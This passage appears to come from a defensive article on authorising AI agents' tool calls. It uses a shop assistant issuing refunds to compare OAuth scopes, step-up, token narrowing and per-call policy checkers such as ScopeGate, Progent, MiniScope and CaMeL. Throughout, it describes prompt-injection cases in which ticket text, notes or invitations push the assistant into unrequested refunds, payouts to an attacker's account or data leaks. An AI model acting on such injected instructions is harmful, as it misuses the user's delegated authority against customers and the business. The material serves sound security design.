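Requesting every scope a plugin publishes seems to contradict least privilege. Model Context Protocol's rationale is that a general-purpose client usually doesn't know what a particular plugin's scopes are for, so the authorisation server and the user are better placed to decide. This reasoning depends on the published list being short. Under the rules, the list should contain only what basic use requires, but the same guidance describes publishing every possible scope as a common mistake. If a plugin's developer makes that mistake and also omits the scopes from the challenge, Maya's first request to look up a delivery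 produces a consent page that asks for refund rights too.

A client that starts with few scopes will sooner or later need another. Suppose the assistant can only read orders and tries to issue a refund. The plugin should refuse with an `insufficient_scope` error that names what is missing:

```http
HTTP/1.1 403 Forbidden
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer error="insufficient_scope",
                         scope="refunds:create"
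```

A client acting for a user should then begin a "step-up", in which it sends the user back to the authorisation server, obtains a token with more scopes and retries the call. A client working without a user may stop instead. Under the rules, clients should limit their retries, because repeated requests will not get a user a scope they have no right to.

The plugin can choose which scope to require based on the call's arguments. For example, it could require `refunds:create` for refunds of up to £100 and `refunds:large` for anything above that. If the authorisation server gave the second scope only to managers, the £900 call would fail for Maya. The plugin's code would still have to compare the amount with the threshold, so the limit would depend on that code as well as the token.

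Common mistakes listed in the Model Context Protocol's guidance include treating the scopes in a token as sufficient, without authorisation logic on the server.

### Why permissions accumulate

During a step-up, the client requests the scopes it has already asked for as well as those in the new challenge.

Soormally's *MCP Scope Step-Up Authorization* describes a test that showed a fault in the official TypeScript SDK. The plugin had one scope for reading employee data and another for changing it. The client began with `employees:read`. When it tried to make a change, the plugin required `employees:write`, and the SDK replaced the old scope with the new one. The next request needed the reading scope again, so the client requested it and lost the writing scope. This cycle repeated, and the browser kept opening new login pages.

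Under the specification at the time, plugins were supposed to prevent this loop by repeating the client's existing scopes in each challenge. Soormally objected that a plugin should only have to report the scopes an operation needs, because the client is the one with a record of the scopes it has collected. The July rules divide the work this way, which fixes the loop but also means that a client's permissions grow each time it steps up.

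Suppose the shop had a single plugin for orders, refunds and customer records:

| Day | Maya's request | Scope in the challenge | Scopes on the new token |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Monday | Look up a delivery | `orders:read` | `orders:read` |
| Tuesday | Refund £40 | `refunds:create` | `orders:read`, `refunds:create` |
| Wednesday | Correct an address | `customers:write` | `orders:read`, `refunds:create`, `customers:write` |

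On Thursday Maya asks about another delivery, and a note on the order contains an instruction to refund £90. The token already has the refund scope, so no consent page appears. On Monday the plugin would have rejected the refund for lack of scope, and Maya would have seen a consent page about refunds after asking only about a delivery, which might have made her suspicious.

The step-up procedure has no way for the client to give up a scope. Each new request includes the scopes that the client requested earlier, even those the authorisation server refused. Splitting the plugin into three would give each token fewer scopes, so a thief could do less with a stolen one. It would not reduce the assistant's own access, because the assistant would hold all three tokens.

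A scope granted earlier also doesn't show whether the user is still present. WorkOS's *MCP* (2026) gives the example of an agent that deletes a production database with a scope its user granted three hours earlier. MCP gives the plugin no standard way to ask for a fresh login first. If the plugin sent `insufficient_scope`, the client would respond by obtaining more permissions, which is the wrong response when the doubt is about the user's presence.

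### Gaps in client support

Narrow initial scopes are practical only if the client can request more scopes later (step-up authorisation). The evidence on this comes mostly from individual developers and vendors' documentation, and the vendors may have since fixed some of the reported problems.

*MCP step‑up consent not exposed for insufficient scope* (gurudatta-stripe, February 2026) reported that the code editor Cursor displayed an insufficient-scope error but offered no way to grant the missing scope. The user had to log out completely and start again. Someone who replied, apparently from Cursor's staff, reported having trouble finding any MCP server that used scopes like this, and said that all the servers they used gave the client the same permissions as the user's account. That is one person's experience, but it suggests that many plugins may not have narrow scopes to request.

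Clients also differ in how they expect a plugin to report a missing scope. MCP uses the HTTP status code, the 403 in the example above. By March 2026, OpenAI's documentation told plugins to return an ordinary tool result marked as an error, with the challenge inside it. In *Mixed Auth & Scope Escalation Dissonance with MCP Spec*, a developer asked which method to follow. Anthropic's *Lazy authentication for MCP servers* warns against the method in OpenAI's documentation, because Claude passes such an error to the model as text and shows the user no login prompt. A plugin that uses one method for every client could therefore work in ChatGPT and fail in Claude, or the reverse.

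Even the standard method did not always work in ChatGPT. In *ChatGPT does not re-trigger OAuth on 401 + WWW-Authenticate*, a developer reports that when a token expired, ChatGPT told the user to log in again but did not open the login page.

Before the July revision, Claude supported step-up but did not fully accumulate scopes. It combined the new challenge with the scopes from the plugin's initial challenge or published list, and Anthropic warned that scopes from an earlier step-up "aren't reliably carried forward". In the shop's example, Wednesday's token might have had `orders:read` and `customers:write` but not `refunds:create`. This would have protected Maya on Thursday by accident, but her next refund would have needed another prompt. At the end of July, Claude's connectors still used the older protocol while Anthropic introduced the new one, according to Zuplo's *claude.ai, Claude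 Desktop, mobile, and Cowork connectors*.

These gaps encourage developers to request broad tokens. If a narrow scope leaves users of a popular client stuck halfway through a task, the plugin's developer can avoid complaints by requesting every permission at the first login.

### Tokens that name an amount and a payee

OAuth already has a more precise alternative in Rich Authorization Requests, or RFC 9396. Instead of a label such as `refunds:create`, the client sends a structured description of what it wants to do in a parameter called `authorization_details`. For Maya's refund it might contain this:

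```json
[
  {
    "type": "shop_refund",
    "actions": ["create"],
    "order": "A-1182",
    "amount": { "currency": "GBP", "value": "40.00" },
    "destination": "original_card"
  }
]
```

The `type` field determines which other fields the object may contain, and the shop would define the `shop_refund` type itself. The authorisation server can show these details to Maya and, if she agrees, record them with the token. The refund plugin then compares each call with the record. It rejects the £900 refund because the amount and destination are wrong. It also rejects the unrequested £90 refund, which an ordinary scope or a £100 ceiling would allow.

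The result depends on the request containing the right values. If the client copies them from the model's tool call, a successful injection produces a request for £900, and the authorisation server or Maya has to catch it. The token alone also doesn't prevent repetition, so the assistant could send the £40 twice if the plugin doesn't record the first refund.

Several commercial login products support the standard, and banking is its best-known use. Plugins cannot rely on it, because MCP's authorisation rules do not build on it. A general-purpose client will therefore not send these details, and a plugin has no agreed way to ask for them. *STEPZ* (Lombardo, 2025) proposed a challenge that would let a service name the missing `authorization_details`, but the draft expired in January 2026.

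Payment companies have built more specific credentials of this kind. Stripe's shared payment tokens let an agent buy something for a customer, and each token specifies a seller, a maximum amount and an expiry time. They are for purchases, so the shop could not use them for refunds.

Another design lets the holder of a token narrow it further without contacting the issuer. Google researchers published the best-known version, macaroons, in 2014. It uses an HMAC, a function that turns a secret and a text into a short code that nobody can produce without the secret. The issuer has a secret *K* and computes a code for a new token. Each added restriction then produces a new code from the previous one:

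*s*₀ = HMAC(*K*, token ID)
*s*₁ = HMAC(*s*₀, "amount ≤ 100")
*s*₂ = HMAC(*s*₁, "order = A-1182")

The token consists of its ID, the list of restrictions and the latest code. Anyone who holds it can add a restriction by computing the next code. Nobody can remove the last restriction from a token that carries *s*₂, because that would require *s*₁, which can't be computed from *s*₂. When the token arrives, the service recomputes the chain from *K* and checks the call against every restriction.

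The shop could use this without showing Maya any prompt. Before the model reads the ticket, the client would take a token for refunds of up to £100 and restrict it to the order number and the original card. The client would then use only this restricted copy for the rest of the task, so nothing in the ticket could widen its permissions. If the model instead chose the restrictions after reading the ticket, the ticket's author could influence them.

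The Python Package Index, which distributes Python software, and the cloud company Fly.io both use macaroons for their API tokens. The MCP specification doesn't include them, so a shop would have to build support into its own client and services.

### Connectors that change after approval

A scope can also come to permit more after the user approves it. The security company PromptArmor monitored 2,517 connectors for Claude and ChatGPT from mid-May to the end of June 2026. Its *Claude and ChatGPT Connectors Change Every 9 Minutes* reports that 931 of them (37%) changed in some way.

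| Change | Number |
| --- | --- |
| New tools on existing connectors | 1,686 |
| Rewritten tool descriptions | 1,127 |
| Tools that accepted different inputs | 664 |
| Newly requested OAuth scopes | 86 |
| Read-only connectors that gained tools able to write | 21 |
| Read-only tools that became able to write | 12 |

News coverage made the permission changes sound worse than they were. In July, Antipov (2026) reported in the headline of a Russian article, *Думаете, что знаете, какие права выдали своему ИИ-агенту?*, that permissions had changed for a third of the connectors. The 37% figure includes connectors that only had a description rewritten, and fewer than 1% went from read-only to being able to write. The new scopes also seem concentrated in a few products. Slack's connector went from 1 scope to 34, Brex's gained 16 and Dropbox's gained 8, which together account for 57 of the 86 new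 scopes.

PromptArmor sells monitoring for such changes, so it has a commercial interest in presenting them as dangerous. It doesn't report that any of them caused harm, but it found that they rarely came with a notice or a new request for consent. New tools are a risk even when the scopes stay the same.

If a connector needs a scope that an existing OAuth token lacks, the user or the company has to authorise it. But a new tool covered by a scope already granted can work immediately. Suppose Maya approved `refunds:create` when the plugin could only return money to the original card, and the developer later adds goodwill payments to any account under the same scope. Her token now allows those payments, although the token itself has not changed. Model Context Protocol's guidance lists silently changing a scope's meaning as a common mistake.

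The shop's limits at the payment company would still apply to these goodwill payments.

### Narrow scopes and repeated prompts

If Maya makes 60 refunds a day and each needs its own token, she might see 60 consent pages. She would soon approve them without reading, so the narrower tokens would achieve little. With one broad scope, she sees a single page, but her approval covers every later refund.

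Model Context Protocol's guidance recommends that a challenge include related scopes that people commonly use together, so that users see fewer prompts. But it also notes that broad requests reduce convenience as well as security. Some users refuse a consent page with a long list of permissions, and revoking a broad token after a theft interrupts everything that depends on it.

The shop can ease the conflict by narrowing a credential without asking Maya. For connectors that employees reach through a company login, Anthropic lets administrators choose which permissions Claude may request and set narrower limits for particular roles. The shop could allow support staff to use `refunds:create` but exclude the scope for goodwill payments, even if the plugin advertises both. A limit set at the payment company or a token that the client narrows itself doesn't require a prompt either.

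This is a reason to put the fixed limits, such as the £100 ceiling and the daily number of refunds, where the shop controls them. Prompts can then be rare enough for Maya to read, for example when the assistant first asks for permission to move money. None of these limits would stop the unrequested £90 refund to the original card, so that call has to be approved or refused individually.

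## How does a per-action authorisation check work?

A per-action authorisation check has two parts. A decision point compares each call with a policy and returns "allow" or "deny". An enforcement point sits between the model and the action, sends every call to the decision point, and lets through only the calls that are allowed. In a small system, both may be a few lines of code in the refund plugin.

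Either part can fail without the other. An attacker can bypass even a perfect shop policy if the plugin has a second entrance without an enforcement point. If every call passes through the enforcement point but the policy permits any destination, the £900 still goes out.

An instruction that forbids the assistant from issuing refunds above £100 is neither of these parts, because the model can still write a call for a larger refund.

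### ScopeGate's five stages

In June 2026 Mellafe Zuvic published ScopeGate, a small check of this kind. It is ordinary code, and no language model takes part in the decision. It receives the proposed call, some trusted context from the application, and a policy written by the operator. In simplified form, it works like this:

```text
decide(call, context, policy):
    if call.tool is not in policy:
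        deny                                 # 1. listed tool
    rule = policy[call.tool]
    for each argument that rule restricts:
        if its value is not in the permitted set:
            deny                             # 2. permitted values
    if rule covers money:
        if not (amount is finite and 0 <= amount <= rule.ceiling):
            deny                             # 3. money ceiling
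    if rule needs an idempotency key and context has none:
        deny                                 # 4. idempotency key
    allow
    on any error: deny                       # 5. denial by default
```

Maya's policy could list `issue_refund`, permit only `original_card` as the destination, set a ceiling of £100 and require an idempotency key.

| Stage | £40 to the original card | £900 to another account |
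| --- | --- | --- |
| Listed tool | Passes | Passes |
| Permitted values | Passes | Fails, because the account is not in the set |
| Money ceiling | Passes | Not reached |
| Idempotency key | Passes if the client supplied one | Not reached |
| Result | Allow | Deny |

If the ticket had specified a £900 refund to the original card, the call would have failed at the money ceiling instead. The unrequested £90 refund to the original card passes every stage because the policy doesn't refer to Maya's request.

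This policy also doesn't restrict the order number, so the assistant could refund £40 on somebody else's order. The shop could allow refunds only on the order attached to the ticket Maya opened, as long as its code takes the order number from the ticket system's record and not from the model. ScopeGate's algorithm uses the context only for the idempotency key, so the shop would have to load a different policy to give Maya's manager a higher refund limit.

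An idempotency key is a string that identifies one intended operation. If a payment service receives the same key twice, it returns the first result instead of paying again. ScopeGate only checks that a key is present, so the payment service still has to recognise the duplicate.

The client also has to reuse the key when the model retries a call. Suppose the £40 refund succeeds but the reply gets lost, and the model writes the call again. If the client creates a new key for every call, the customer receives £80. *Beyond Single-Use Tokens* (2026) calls this "semantic replay" and shows that single-use tokens don't prevent it, because each repeated call can obtain a fresh token. It proposes keeping a lasting record of the original authorisation and counting every attempt against it, whichever token the attempt carries.

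### What three toolkits check by default

Mellafe Zuvic audited the public code of LangChain, its companion LangGraph, and LlamaIndex, which developers use to build agents, and of the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to Stripe's payment service. The aim was to find code that runs after the model has written a call and refuses unauthorised argument values before the call takes effect.

| Toolkit | Default control | Treatment of argument values |
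| --- | --- | --- |
| LangChain and LangGraph | Looks up the tool by name and usually checks the arguments' types | Passes them to the tool. Callbacks can observe the call but cannot reliably veto it |
| LlamaIndex | Looks up the tool by name | Passes them to the tool. A person approves only if the tool's author built that step |
| Stripe Agent Toolkit | Applies a list of allowed actions and the permissions of the Stripe key | Forwards values such as the amount and the customer |

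All three limit which tools the model can call, but by default none authorises the values in those calls. To show the consequence, Mellafe Zuvic gave LangChain a fixed call to change a merchant's payout account to an attacker's. LangChain ran it against a simulated payment system, and the account changed. ScopeGate denied the same call because the new account was not in the permitted set.

The paper does not present these defaults as security bugs. The toolkits leave authorisation to the developer, who can add a check, and LangChain has optional middleware for human approval. The audit covers particular versions from mid-2026, so a developer using a later release should look at what it does between reading the model's call and running the tool.

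The finding about Stripe also covers only the toolkit's public code, not Stripe's remote MCP server. Stripe applies its own rules on refund size when a request reaches it, whatever the toolkit forwards.

### How far the ScopeGate tests reach

| Test | Unauthorised calls | Result |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Fixed bypass attempts | 48 | ScopeGate allowed none |
| 40 rounds against an adaptive attacker | 29 | ScopeGate allowed none |
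| Ten legitimate calls from two models | 0 | ScopeGate wrongly denied none |
| Ten payment trials with Latam-GPT | 10 | ScopeGate allowed none |

The fixed attempts included account names with invisible characters or lookalike letters, misspelt tool names, arguments of the wrong type, strange amounts and missing idempotency keys. In the adaptive run, another language model, GLM-5.2, made the attacks. It received ScopeGate's reason for each denial and tried again. Nine of GLM-5.2's other 11 calls were malformed, and two were legitimate calls that ScopeGate allowed.

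The fixed attempts exposed a flaw in an earlier prototype. Software represents invalid numerical results as NaN ("not a number"), and a test of whether NaN is greater or less than something is always false. A rule that denies any amount greater than 100 therefore lets NaN through. The repaired code denies the call unless the amount is between zero and the limit.

These tests are good evidence that the code handles those inputs correctly, but much weaker evidence of how it would perform in a working shop. In the payout tests, the permitted set contained a single account, and a program that compares strings exactly should reject every other string. Deciding what belongs in the set is harder when thousands of customers have different cards and orders. The same person wrote both the control and the bypass attempts, so an outsider might find another mistake like the one with NaN.

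Ten legitimate calls are too few to estimate how often the check would wrongly deny one. Even if the ten were a random sample of a shop's refunds, seeing no denials would be consistent with a true wrongful-denial rate as high as 26% (at 95% confidence). At that rate, a shop that makes 40 refunds a day would have about ten of them wrongly denied.

### Keeping the policy out of the model's reach

ScopeGate stops the payout because text the model reads can change the account in the call but not the set of permitted accounts. If the model also supplied the set, the attacker could change both so that they matched, and the payout would pass the check.

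Mellafe Zuvic therefore requires that no part of the policy come from a model's output, directly or indirectly, and that the policy stay fixed during a conversation. Indirect routes are easy to miss. For example, if the shop builds its list of permitted accounts from customer records that the assistant can edit, one ticket could make the assistant add an account and a second could request a refund to it.

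The rule even excludes a policy that a model drafts in advance. This seems stricter than the argument requires, because an engineer who reviews each line of the draft decides what goes into the policy.

A fixed policy also has to permit everything any of Maya's tasks might need. She sometimes has to refund £90, so the policy permits a £90 refund on every ticket. The check can refuse £90 on a ticket that merits £40 only if it has a policy specific to that task.

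### Progent's policies for each task

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) has a language model write that policy. The model first sees only the user's request and the list of tools, and writes rules about tool names and argument values. Ordinary code then checks each tool call and denies any that no rule allows.

Many requests don't contain enough information to determine which actions to allow. If a user says "deal with this ticket", the policy can safely allow the assistant to read the ticket, but the request gives no basis for allowing any particular refund. Progent therefore lets the model propose a new policy after reading a tool's result, which may contain an injection.

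This is the circularity that Mellafe Zuvic warns about, and Surapani and colleagues raise the same objection to any design in which the governed model specifies its own limits. Progent's answer is to compare the old and new policies with a solver, a program that can determine whether a logical formula holds in every case. Let *A*(*P*) be the set of calls that a policy *P* allows. Progent applies a new policy *P*′ automatically only if

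*A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*),

which means that the new policy allows nothing the old one forbade. Any other change is an expansion, and somebody has to approve it. An injection can therefore fool the model that writes the policy without silently giving the agent new permissions.

In Maya's case, the policy after her request allows only reading the ticket. After reading it, the model should propose adding a £40 refund to the original card. If the injection succeeds, the model proposes adding the £900 refund instead. The solver classifies both as expansions because it tests only whether permissions have grown. Maya, or whoever approves the change, has to judge whether they should have. If she had typed the order, the amount and the card herself, the first policy could have contained exactly that refund, and both the £90 and the £900 refunds would have needed approval.

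Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo and on ASB, another set of simulated attacks on agents.

| Test | Successful attacks without Progent | With Progent |
| --- | --- | --- |
| AgentDojo | 39.9% | 1.0% |
| ASB | 70.3% | 3.9% |
| AgentDojo, first policy never updated | 39.9% | 2.5% |
| AgentDojo, a person reviews the first policy and every expansion | 39.9% | 0% |

The agents completed about as many legitimate tasks as before. However, in the runs that produced the 1.0% and 3.9% attack rates, Progent approved every expansion automatically to imitate a careless user. The solver therefore blocked nothing, and the improvement came from the policies that GPT-4o wrote. This makes the low attack rates stronger evidence of GPT-4o's ability to write policies, but the guarantee against silent expansion did not contribute to them.

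Only 6% of policy updates on AgentDojo were expansions, which suggests that approvals would be rare, though the shop would probably need them more often. The AgentDojo runs gave agents standing permission for harmless read-only tools, and many of the tasks stated their goal clearly. When Maya hands over a ticket with a vague request, the assistant would almost always need an expansion before it could pay anything.

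*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (March 2026) objected that hostile tool results might loosen Progent's policy through its updates. The objection may concern an earlier version, because the May 2026 version requires approval by default whenever the policy expands. It still applies to anyone who sets that approval to automatic. Progent also assumes that the user's own request is harmless, which isn't true if Maya clicked a link that filled in the prompt for her.

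*ToolFence* (2026) keeps untrusted content from the model that writes the policy. That model receives the user's request and the tool schemas, and specifies in advance what evidence each call needs and how many times the call may run. Separate code then checks each proposed call against those conditions.

Progent can also combine a task's policy with fixed rules from the shop, which take priority. The shop must word these rules carefully, because one that allows refunds up to £100 would make Progent approve the £90 refund without checking the task's policy. A rule that forbids refunds above £100 would still leave smaller refunds to the task's policy.

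### MiniScope's smallest set of scopes

Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025), in *MiniScope*, leave the choice of permissions to arithmetic. MiniScope reads a service's public documentation to learn which OAuth scopes cover which operations. The agent submits a plan of the calls it wants to make, and MiniScope finds the cheapest set of scopes that covers the plan:

minimise Σ cost(*s*) × *x*ₛ

Here *x*ₛ is 1 if the set includes scope *s* and 0 otherwise. Each planned call must be covered by at least one chosen scope, and a scope carries a higher penalty if it permits more operations. The calculation is necessary because scopes overlap. In Google Calendar, 24 of the 37 operations can each be authorised by more than one scope.

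If the plan needs a scope the user hasn't granted, MiniScope asks her to allow it once, for the session, or always. The agent never holds her real credentials. It sends its calls with a session token, and MiniScope checks each call against the granted scopes and attaches the real credential only if they cover it.

The check added 1–6% to the running time. Proprietary language models given the same job found the smallest set of scopes in 70–83% of cases, while open models did so in 20–34%. Zhu and colleagues also applied the method to connectors in ChatGPT and Claude and found six that requested more access than they needed. For example, ChatGPT's Gmail connector asked for scopes covering 50 operations when its tools needed only 32. The tests used synthetic user requests, and simulated users answered the permission prompts, so the results give little indication of how carefully real people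 would answer.

No model chooses the permissions, which avoids part of the circularity. But the agent produces the plan, and an injection can add a step to it. In the paper's example, an email contains an instruction to delete it after replying. The new step needs wider access to the mailbox, so the user sees an unexpected request and can refuse.

The £900 refund would produce no such request, because it uses the same operation and needs the same scope as the £40 refund. Zhu and colleagues explicitly exclude attacks that change only the arguments. MiniScope therefore automates the choice of narrow tokens, but the shop would still need a check on each refund.

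There may also be no single smallest set. One scope might cover refunds and customer addresses, and another refunds and stock levels, so neither contains the other. MiniScope picks by cost, and *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) notes that Zhu and colleagues do not discuss whether the answer is unique. If it isn't unique, the choice depends on how the developer weighs one kind of access against another.

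Attack success rate is an incomplete measure of any of these systems. *Ajar* (2026) measures how many unnecessary calls a defence would allow, weighted by the harm they could do, and how many necessary calls it would permit. On AgentDojo, two of the five defences tested allowed almost equal amounts of excess permission but differed by 37 percentage points in the share of legitimate tasks they completed. A shop could therefore choose a defence that is much worse at handling tickets than another and no better at limiting excess permission.

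### In the client, a gateway or the service

The same decision code gives different protection depending on where the shop runs it.

| Place | Information available | How a bad call can get past |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Client | Maya's request, the ticket and all earlier calls | Another program or agent calls the refund plugin directly |
| Gateway in front of all plugins | The credential, the tool and its arguments | A caller reaches the plugin by another route, or the client uses a built-in tool that skips the gateway |
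| Refund plugin | The shop's orders, Maya's limit and earlier refunds | Another program uses the payment key |
| Payment company | The shop's key, the amount and the destination | The call fits the shop's limits but exceeds Maya's |

A check in the client has the most information about the task. It can compare the refund with what Maya typed, but it covers only the calls that this client makes. A check at the payment company covers every refund made through its service, but the company may not know who Maya is and has probably never seen the ticket.

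Surapani and colleagues give the example of an assistant that summarises a week's meetings. One invitation contains a request to send the user's salary details to an outside address. A check in the client's software can refuse this request because it came from an invitation and the user asked only for a summary. An email gateway receives a valid token and an outside address, so without more information about the task, it must either block all outside email or let this message through.

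Ease of installation also affects the choice of where to run the check. Progent offers both a library, which developers build into an agent, and a proxy (a form of gateway), which users can add without changing the agent's code. The proxy can't check calls to the agent's built-in tools, because those calls never leave the agent. The library can check them, but only a developer can install it. ScopeGate can run in the application, in a small program beside it or in a central gateway, although Mellafe Zuvic tested it only in the application.

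The shop can check refunds in several places. The payment company can enforce a ceiling for everyone, the refund plugin can enforce Maya's limit and look up the original card, and the client can compare the refund with her request. If the client's check fails, the loss stays within the other two limits. These checks add some delay. According to Surapani and colleagues, a lookup in a fixed table takes microseconds, while a policy based on the task and the origin of each argument may take tens or hundreds of milliseconds, and an agent may make hundreds of calls in a session.

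### Arguments made of free text

A policy can list the permitted destinations for a refund, but it can't list every acceptable email to a customer. Surapani and colleagues give the example of an email that passes every type check even though its text contains customer data from a different task.

Progent's rules can test text against a pattern, but the policy in the paper's main example restricts a Slack message to one recipient and allows any text in the body. Patterns can catch text with a regular form, such as a card number, but are much less useful for catching a sentence that reveals a salary.

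The shop can avoid the problem for routine messages by removing the free text. Instead of `send_email(recipient, body)`, the plugin could offer `send_refund_notice(order)`, look up the customer's address and the amount, and fill in a standard letter. An injection could then at most cause the wrong standard letter to go out. But the assistant could no longer answer an unusual question in its own words.

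Some free-text arguments are instructions to a computer. A plugin that accepts any database command has one text argument, which may look up one order or delete the whole table. Offering separate operations, or using a read-only database account, is safer than trying to block every dangerous command with a pattern. When neither is possible, the remaining option is to track where the text came from.

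### Permitted calls that add up

Ten refunds of £90 come to £900, and ScopeGate would allow each of them. To stop the series, the policy needs totals as well as a ceiling for each call:

```text
deny if refunded(order) + amount > price_paid(order)
deny if refunded_today(Maya) + amount > 500
```

The order rule catches repeated refunds on one purchase, and the daily rule catches refunds spread across many orders. Both depend on records of earlier refunds, which the tool call does not contain. *AGATE* (2026) keeps such records. An AGATE authorisation can have a limit for each call, a limit on the remaining total and a number of uses. AGATE deducts from the total when it approves a call, before the tool runs, so repeating a call that fails does not get around the limit. For the same reason, a refund the payment company rejects may still use up part of Maya's allowance.

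When calls use up a limited authority, a more generous policy can make an honest task fail. Suppose the assistant can pay out up to £100 on a ticket that merits an £80 refund, and the shop then allows goodwill payments from the same £100. If the assistant first pays £30 as goodwill, only £70 is left, which is too little for the refund. In *Agenra*, Shivakumar, Priya and Gao (2026) built a policy language that checks a revision for this effect before the developer applies it. In a test on 51 revisions they had written, the checks certified all 21 that preserved the existing tasks and none of the 30 that broke one.

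Totals don't help when the harm comes from a combination of different calls. The assistant is allowed to read another customer's record to compare two orders, and to email the customer who opened the ticket. If it reads the record and then sends the email, it can disclose that record in the email. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) calls this a cumulative violation, one that a program can recognise only by relating a call to earlier events. A screen that highlights the email's recipient would not reveal the violation, because the recipient is correct.

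*AgentCap* (2026) lets a developer forbid combinations of permissions within a session. The shop could bar an assistant that has opened a second customer's record from sending email until the session ends. This would stop the leak, but it would also block a legitimate reply to a customer who asked about an order she had placed from two accounts. The developer must also anticipate each dangerous combination, and a rule limited to one session would miss a record that the assistant saved to memory and emailed the next day.

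### Changes between the check and the payment

A correct authorisation decision can become wrong before the payment is made. Suppose Maya has a daily refund limit of £500 and has already refunded £460, and two copies of the assistant each propose a £40 refund. If both checks run before either refund is recorded, each calculates a total of £500 and allows the refund, which brings the actual total to £540.

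*Stateful Governance for Concurrent Agentic Systems* (Peng and Wu, 2026) calls this stale authorisation. In one experiment, 256 transfers competed for a budget that could cover only 50. When the program checked the budget and then made the transfer as a separate step, about 80 went through. The policy engine Cedar did no better when the calling program supplied the running total, because Cedar couldn't control changes to the total after it returned a decision.

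Treating the check and the payment as one step fixes this. A single lock on the whole system does this, but it makes unrelated refunds wait for each other. Peng and Wu's system, MasuGate, locks only the records a policy depends on, such as one team's budget. It let exactly 50 transfers through. When each operation took 10 milliseconds, it handled about 86 a second, compared with 53 for the single lock.

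Waiting for human approval makes the interval much longer. Suppose a manager takes an hour to approve a refund and others use up the budget in the meantime. Paying on the old approval would exceed the budget, while checking again and refusing would discard the manager's approval. MasuGate can instead reserve the amount while the request is pending. In a test with competing requests, checking again invalidated every pending approval, while reservations preserved them all.

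These experiments used scripted requests instead of a language model, and kept the shared budgets in MasuGate's own database. A payment company holds the shop's money, so the shop could not update the limit and make the payment in one database transaction. It could reserve £40 of Maya's limit, send the refund, and release the reservation only after confirming that the refund had failed. If the reply never arrived, the shop would have to keep the reservation and ask the payment company whether the refund went through.

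### Seven requirements and what remains unmet

Surapani and colleagues propose seven requirements for authorising agents and rate several arrangements against them. One of these, in which a single organisation uses MCP plugins with OAuth, is much like the shop's.

| Requirement | In Maya's case | Coverage by MCP with OAuth |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Attributability | Every refund can be traced to Maya | Partial |
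| Explicit delegation | A record sets out what she delegated | Substantial |
| Monotonic attenuation | No agent passes on more authority than it received | None |
| Aggregation bounds | The assistant cannot combine more information than the ticket requires | None |
| Temporal validity | Authority ends with the task | Substantial |
| Runtime enforcement | An independent check can stop any call | Substantial |
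| Tamper-resistant audit | Nobody can quietly change the record | Partial |

Some of these ratings look generous from the shop's point of view. Runtime enforcement counts as substantial because the plugin validates the token and its scopes on every request, but that check would let the £900 through. The shop has to add its own check on the argument values. Temporal validity counts as substantial because tokens expire, but they expire at a set time and may outlast the ticket by an hour.

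Aggregation bounds are the least developed. The requirement concerns combined information, so a daily limit on refunds doesn't meet it. None of the ten families of mechanism in the review covers it more than partially. Rules that forbid certain combinations, like AgentCap's, help with the cases a developer foresees, but they don't measure how much the assistant has learned relative to what the task needs.

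The ratings also fall sharply when work crosses between organisations. An example constructed by Surapani and colleagues, in which one company's agent passes a task to another's, met none of the seven. The shop has a mild form of this problem with its payment company, which can't verify Maya's part in a refund and keeps a separate log.

They trace several of the gaps to one cause, which is that components pass each other a credential but no description of the task.

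## Can a check take account of where an argument came from?

Suppose the shop lets its assistant email any customer. Maya asks it to write to one customer about the £40 refund, but a line in the ticket gives another customer's address for the message. A check on values, such as ScopeGate's, allows the email because the address is in the permitted set. The shop would want to refuse it because the address came from the ticket instead of the customer's record.

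Broader controls have the same gap. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) notes that a system that permits outgoing email also permits a plausible email produced by an injection. To block the injected email and still allow legitimate ones, a program needs a record of where each argument came from, known as its provenance.

### Labels and how they spread

Information-flow control, a technique from the 1970s, keeps this record by attaching a label to each piece of data and working out a label for everything derived from it. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use two kinds of label. An integrity label marks data as trusted (T) or untrusted (U), and a confidentiality label lists the people who may read it. When a program combines two pieces of data, the result gets the more restrictive label, which the symbol ⊔ denotes:

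T ⊔ U = U

{Maya, manager, accountant} ⊔ {manager, accountant, courier} = {manager, accountant}

Anything that contains untrusted data is therefore untrusted, and only people who may read both sources may read a text made from them.

In the shop, Maya's request is trusted and the customer's text in the ticket is not. A rule that the refund's destination must come from a trusted source would block the account number in the ticket without the shop having to list any accounts.

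Language models make such rules hard to apply. Nobody can say exactly which parts of a model's input led it to write a particular call, so the call has to carry the combined label of everything the model has read. Once the ticket is in the conversation, every later call is untrusted, including the correct £40 refund. Costa and colleagues measured the effect using GPT-4o on AgentDojo, the simulated workplace benchmark, with no attacks. An ordinary agent completed 93.3% of the team-chat tasks, compared with 20.0% when they labelled the whole conversation this way and enforced their rules.

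One remedy is to find out which messages influenced an answer and regenerate it from those alone. Two better-known systems, CaMeL and FIDES, instead keep untrusted text away from the model that chooses the calls.

### CaMeL's plan for a refund

Both systems build on *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023), which proposes splitting an assistant into two models. A privileged model can use tools but never reads untrusted content, while a quarantined model reads that content but has no tools. The privileged model refers to the quarantined model's answers by name, as in "display `$email-summary-1`", without seeing the text.

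Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues at Google DeepMind found a weakness in this design in 2025. Willison (2025) explains it using their example in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. A user asks an assistant to send Bob a document and says that Bob's address is in the meeting notes. The quarantined model reads the notes to find the address. If an attacker has planted an instruction there, the model may return the attacker's address, and the assistant sends the document there even though it followed the right steps.

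CaMeL, the system they built, adds labels to Willison's pattern. It would deal with Maya's ticket in four steps:

1. The privileged model receives Maya's request, the shop's standing instructions and the tool descriptions, but not the ticket. It writes a short program in a restricted version of Python.
2. An interpreter, the software that runs this program, fetches the ticket and stores it in a variable. It labels the customer's text as untrusted.
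3. The quarantined model reads the ticket and returns an amount, which inherits the untrusted label.
4. Before the refund, the interpreter checks the call, its arguments and their labels against a policy.

The program might look like this:

```python
ticket = read_ticket("T-730")
order = get_order(ticket.order_id)
amount = ask_quarantined_model(
    "What refund is due on this order?",
    [ticket, order], output=Number)
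issue_refund(order.id, amount, destination="original_card")
```

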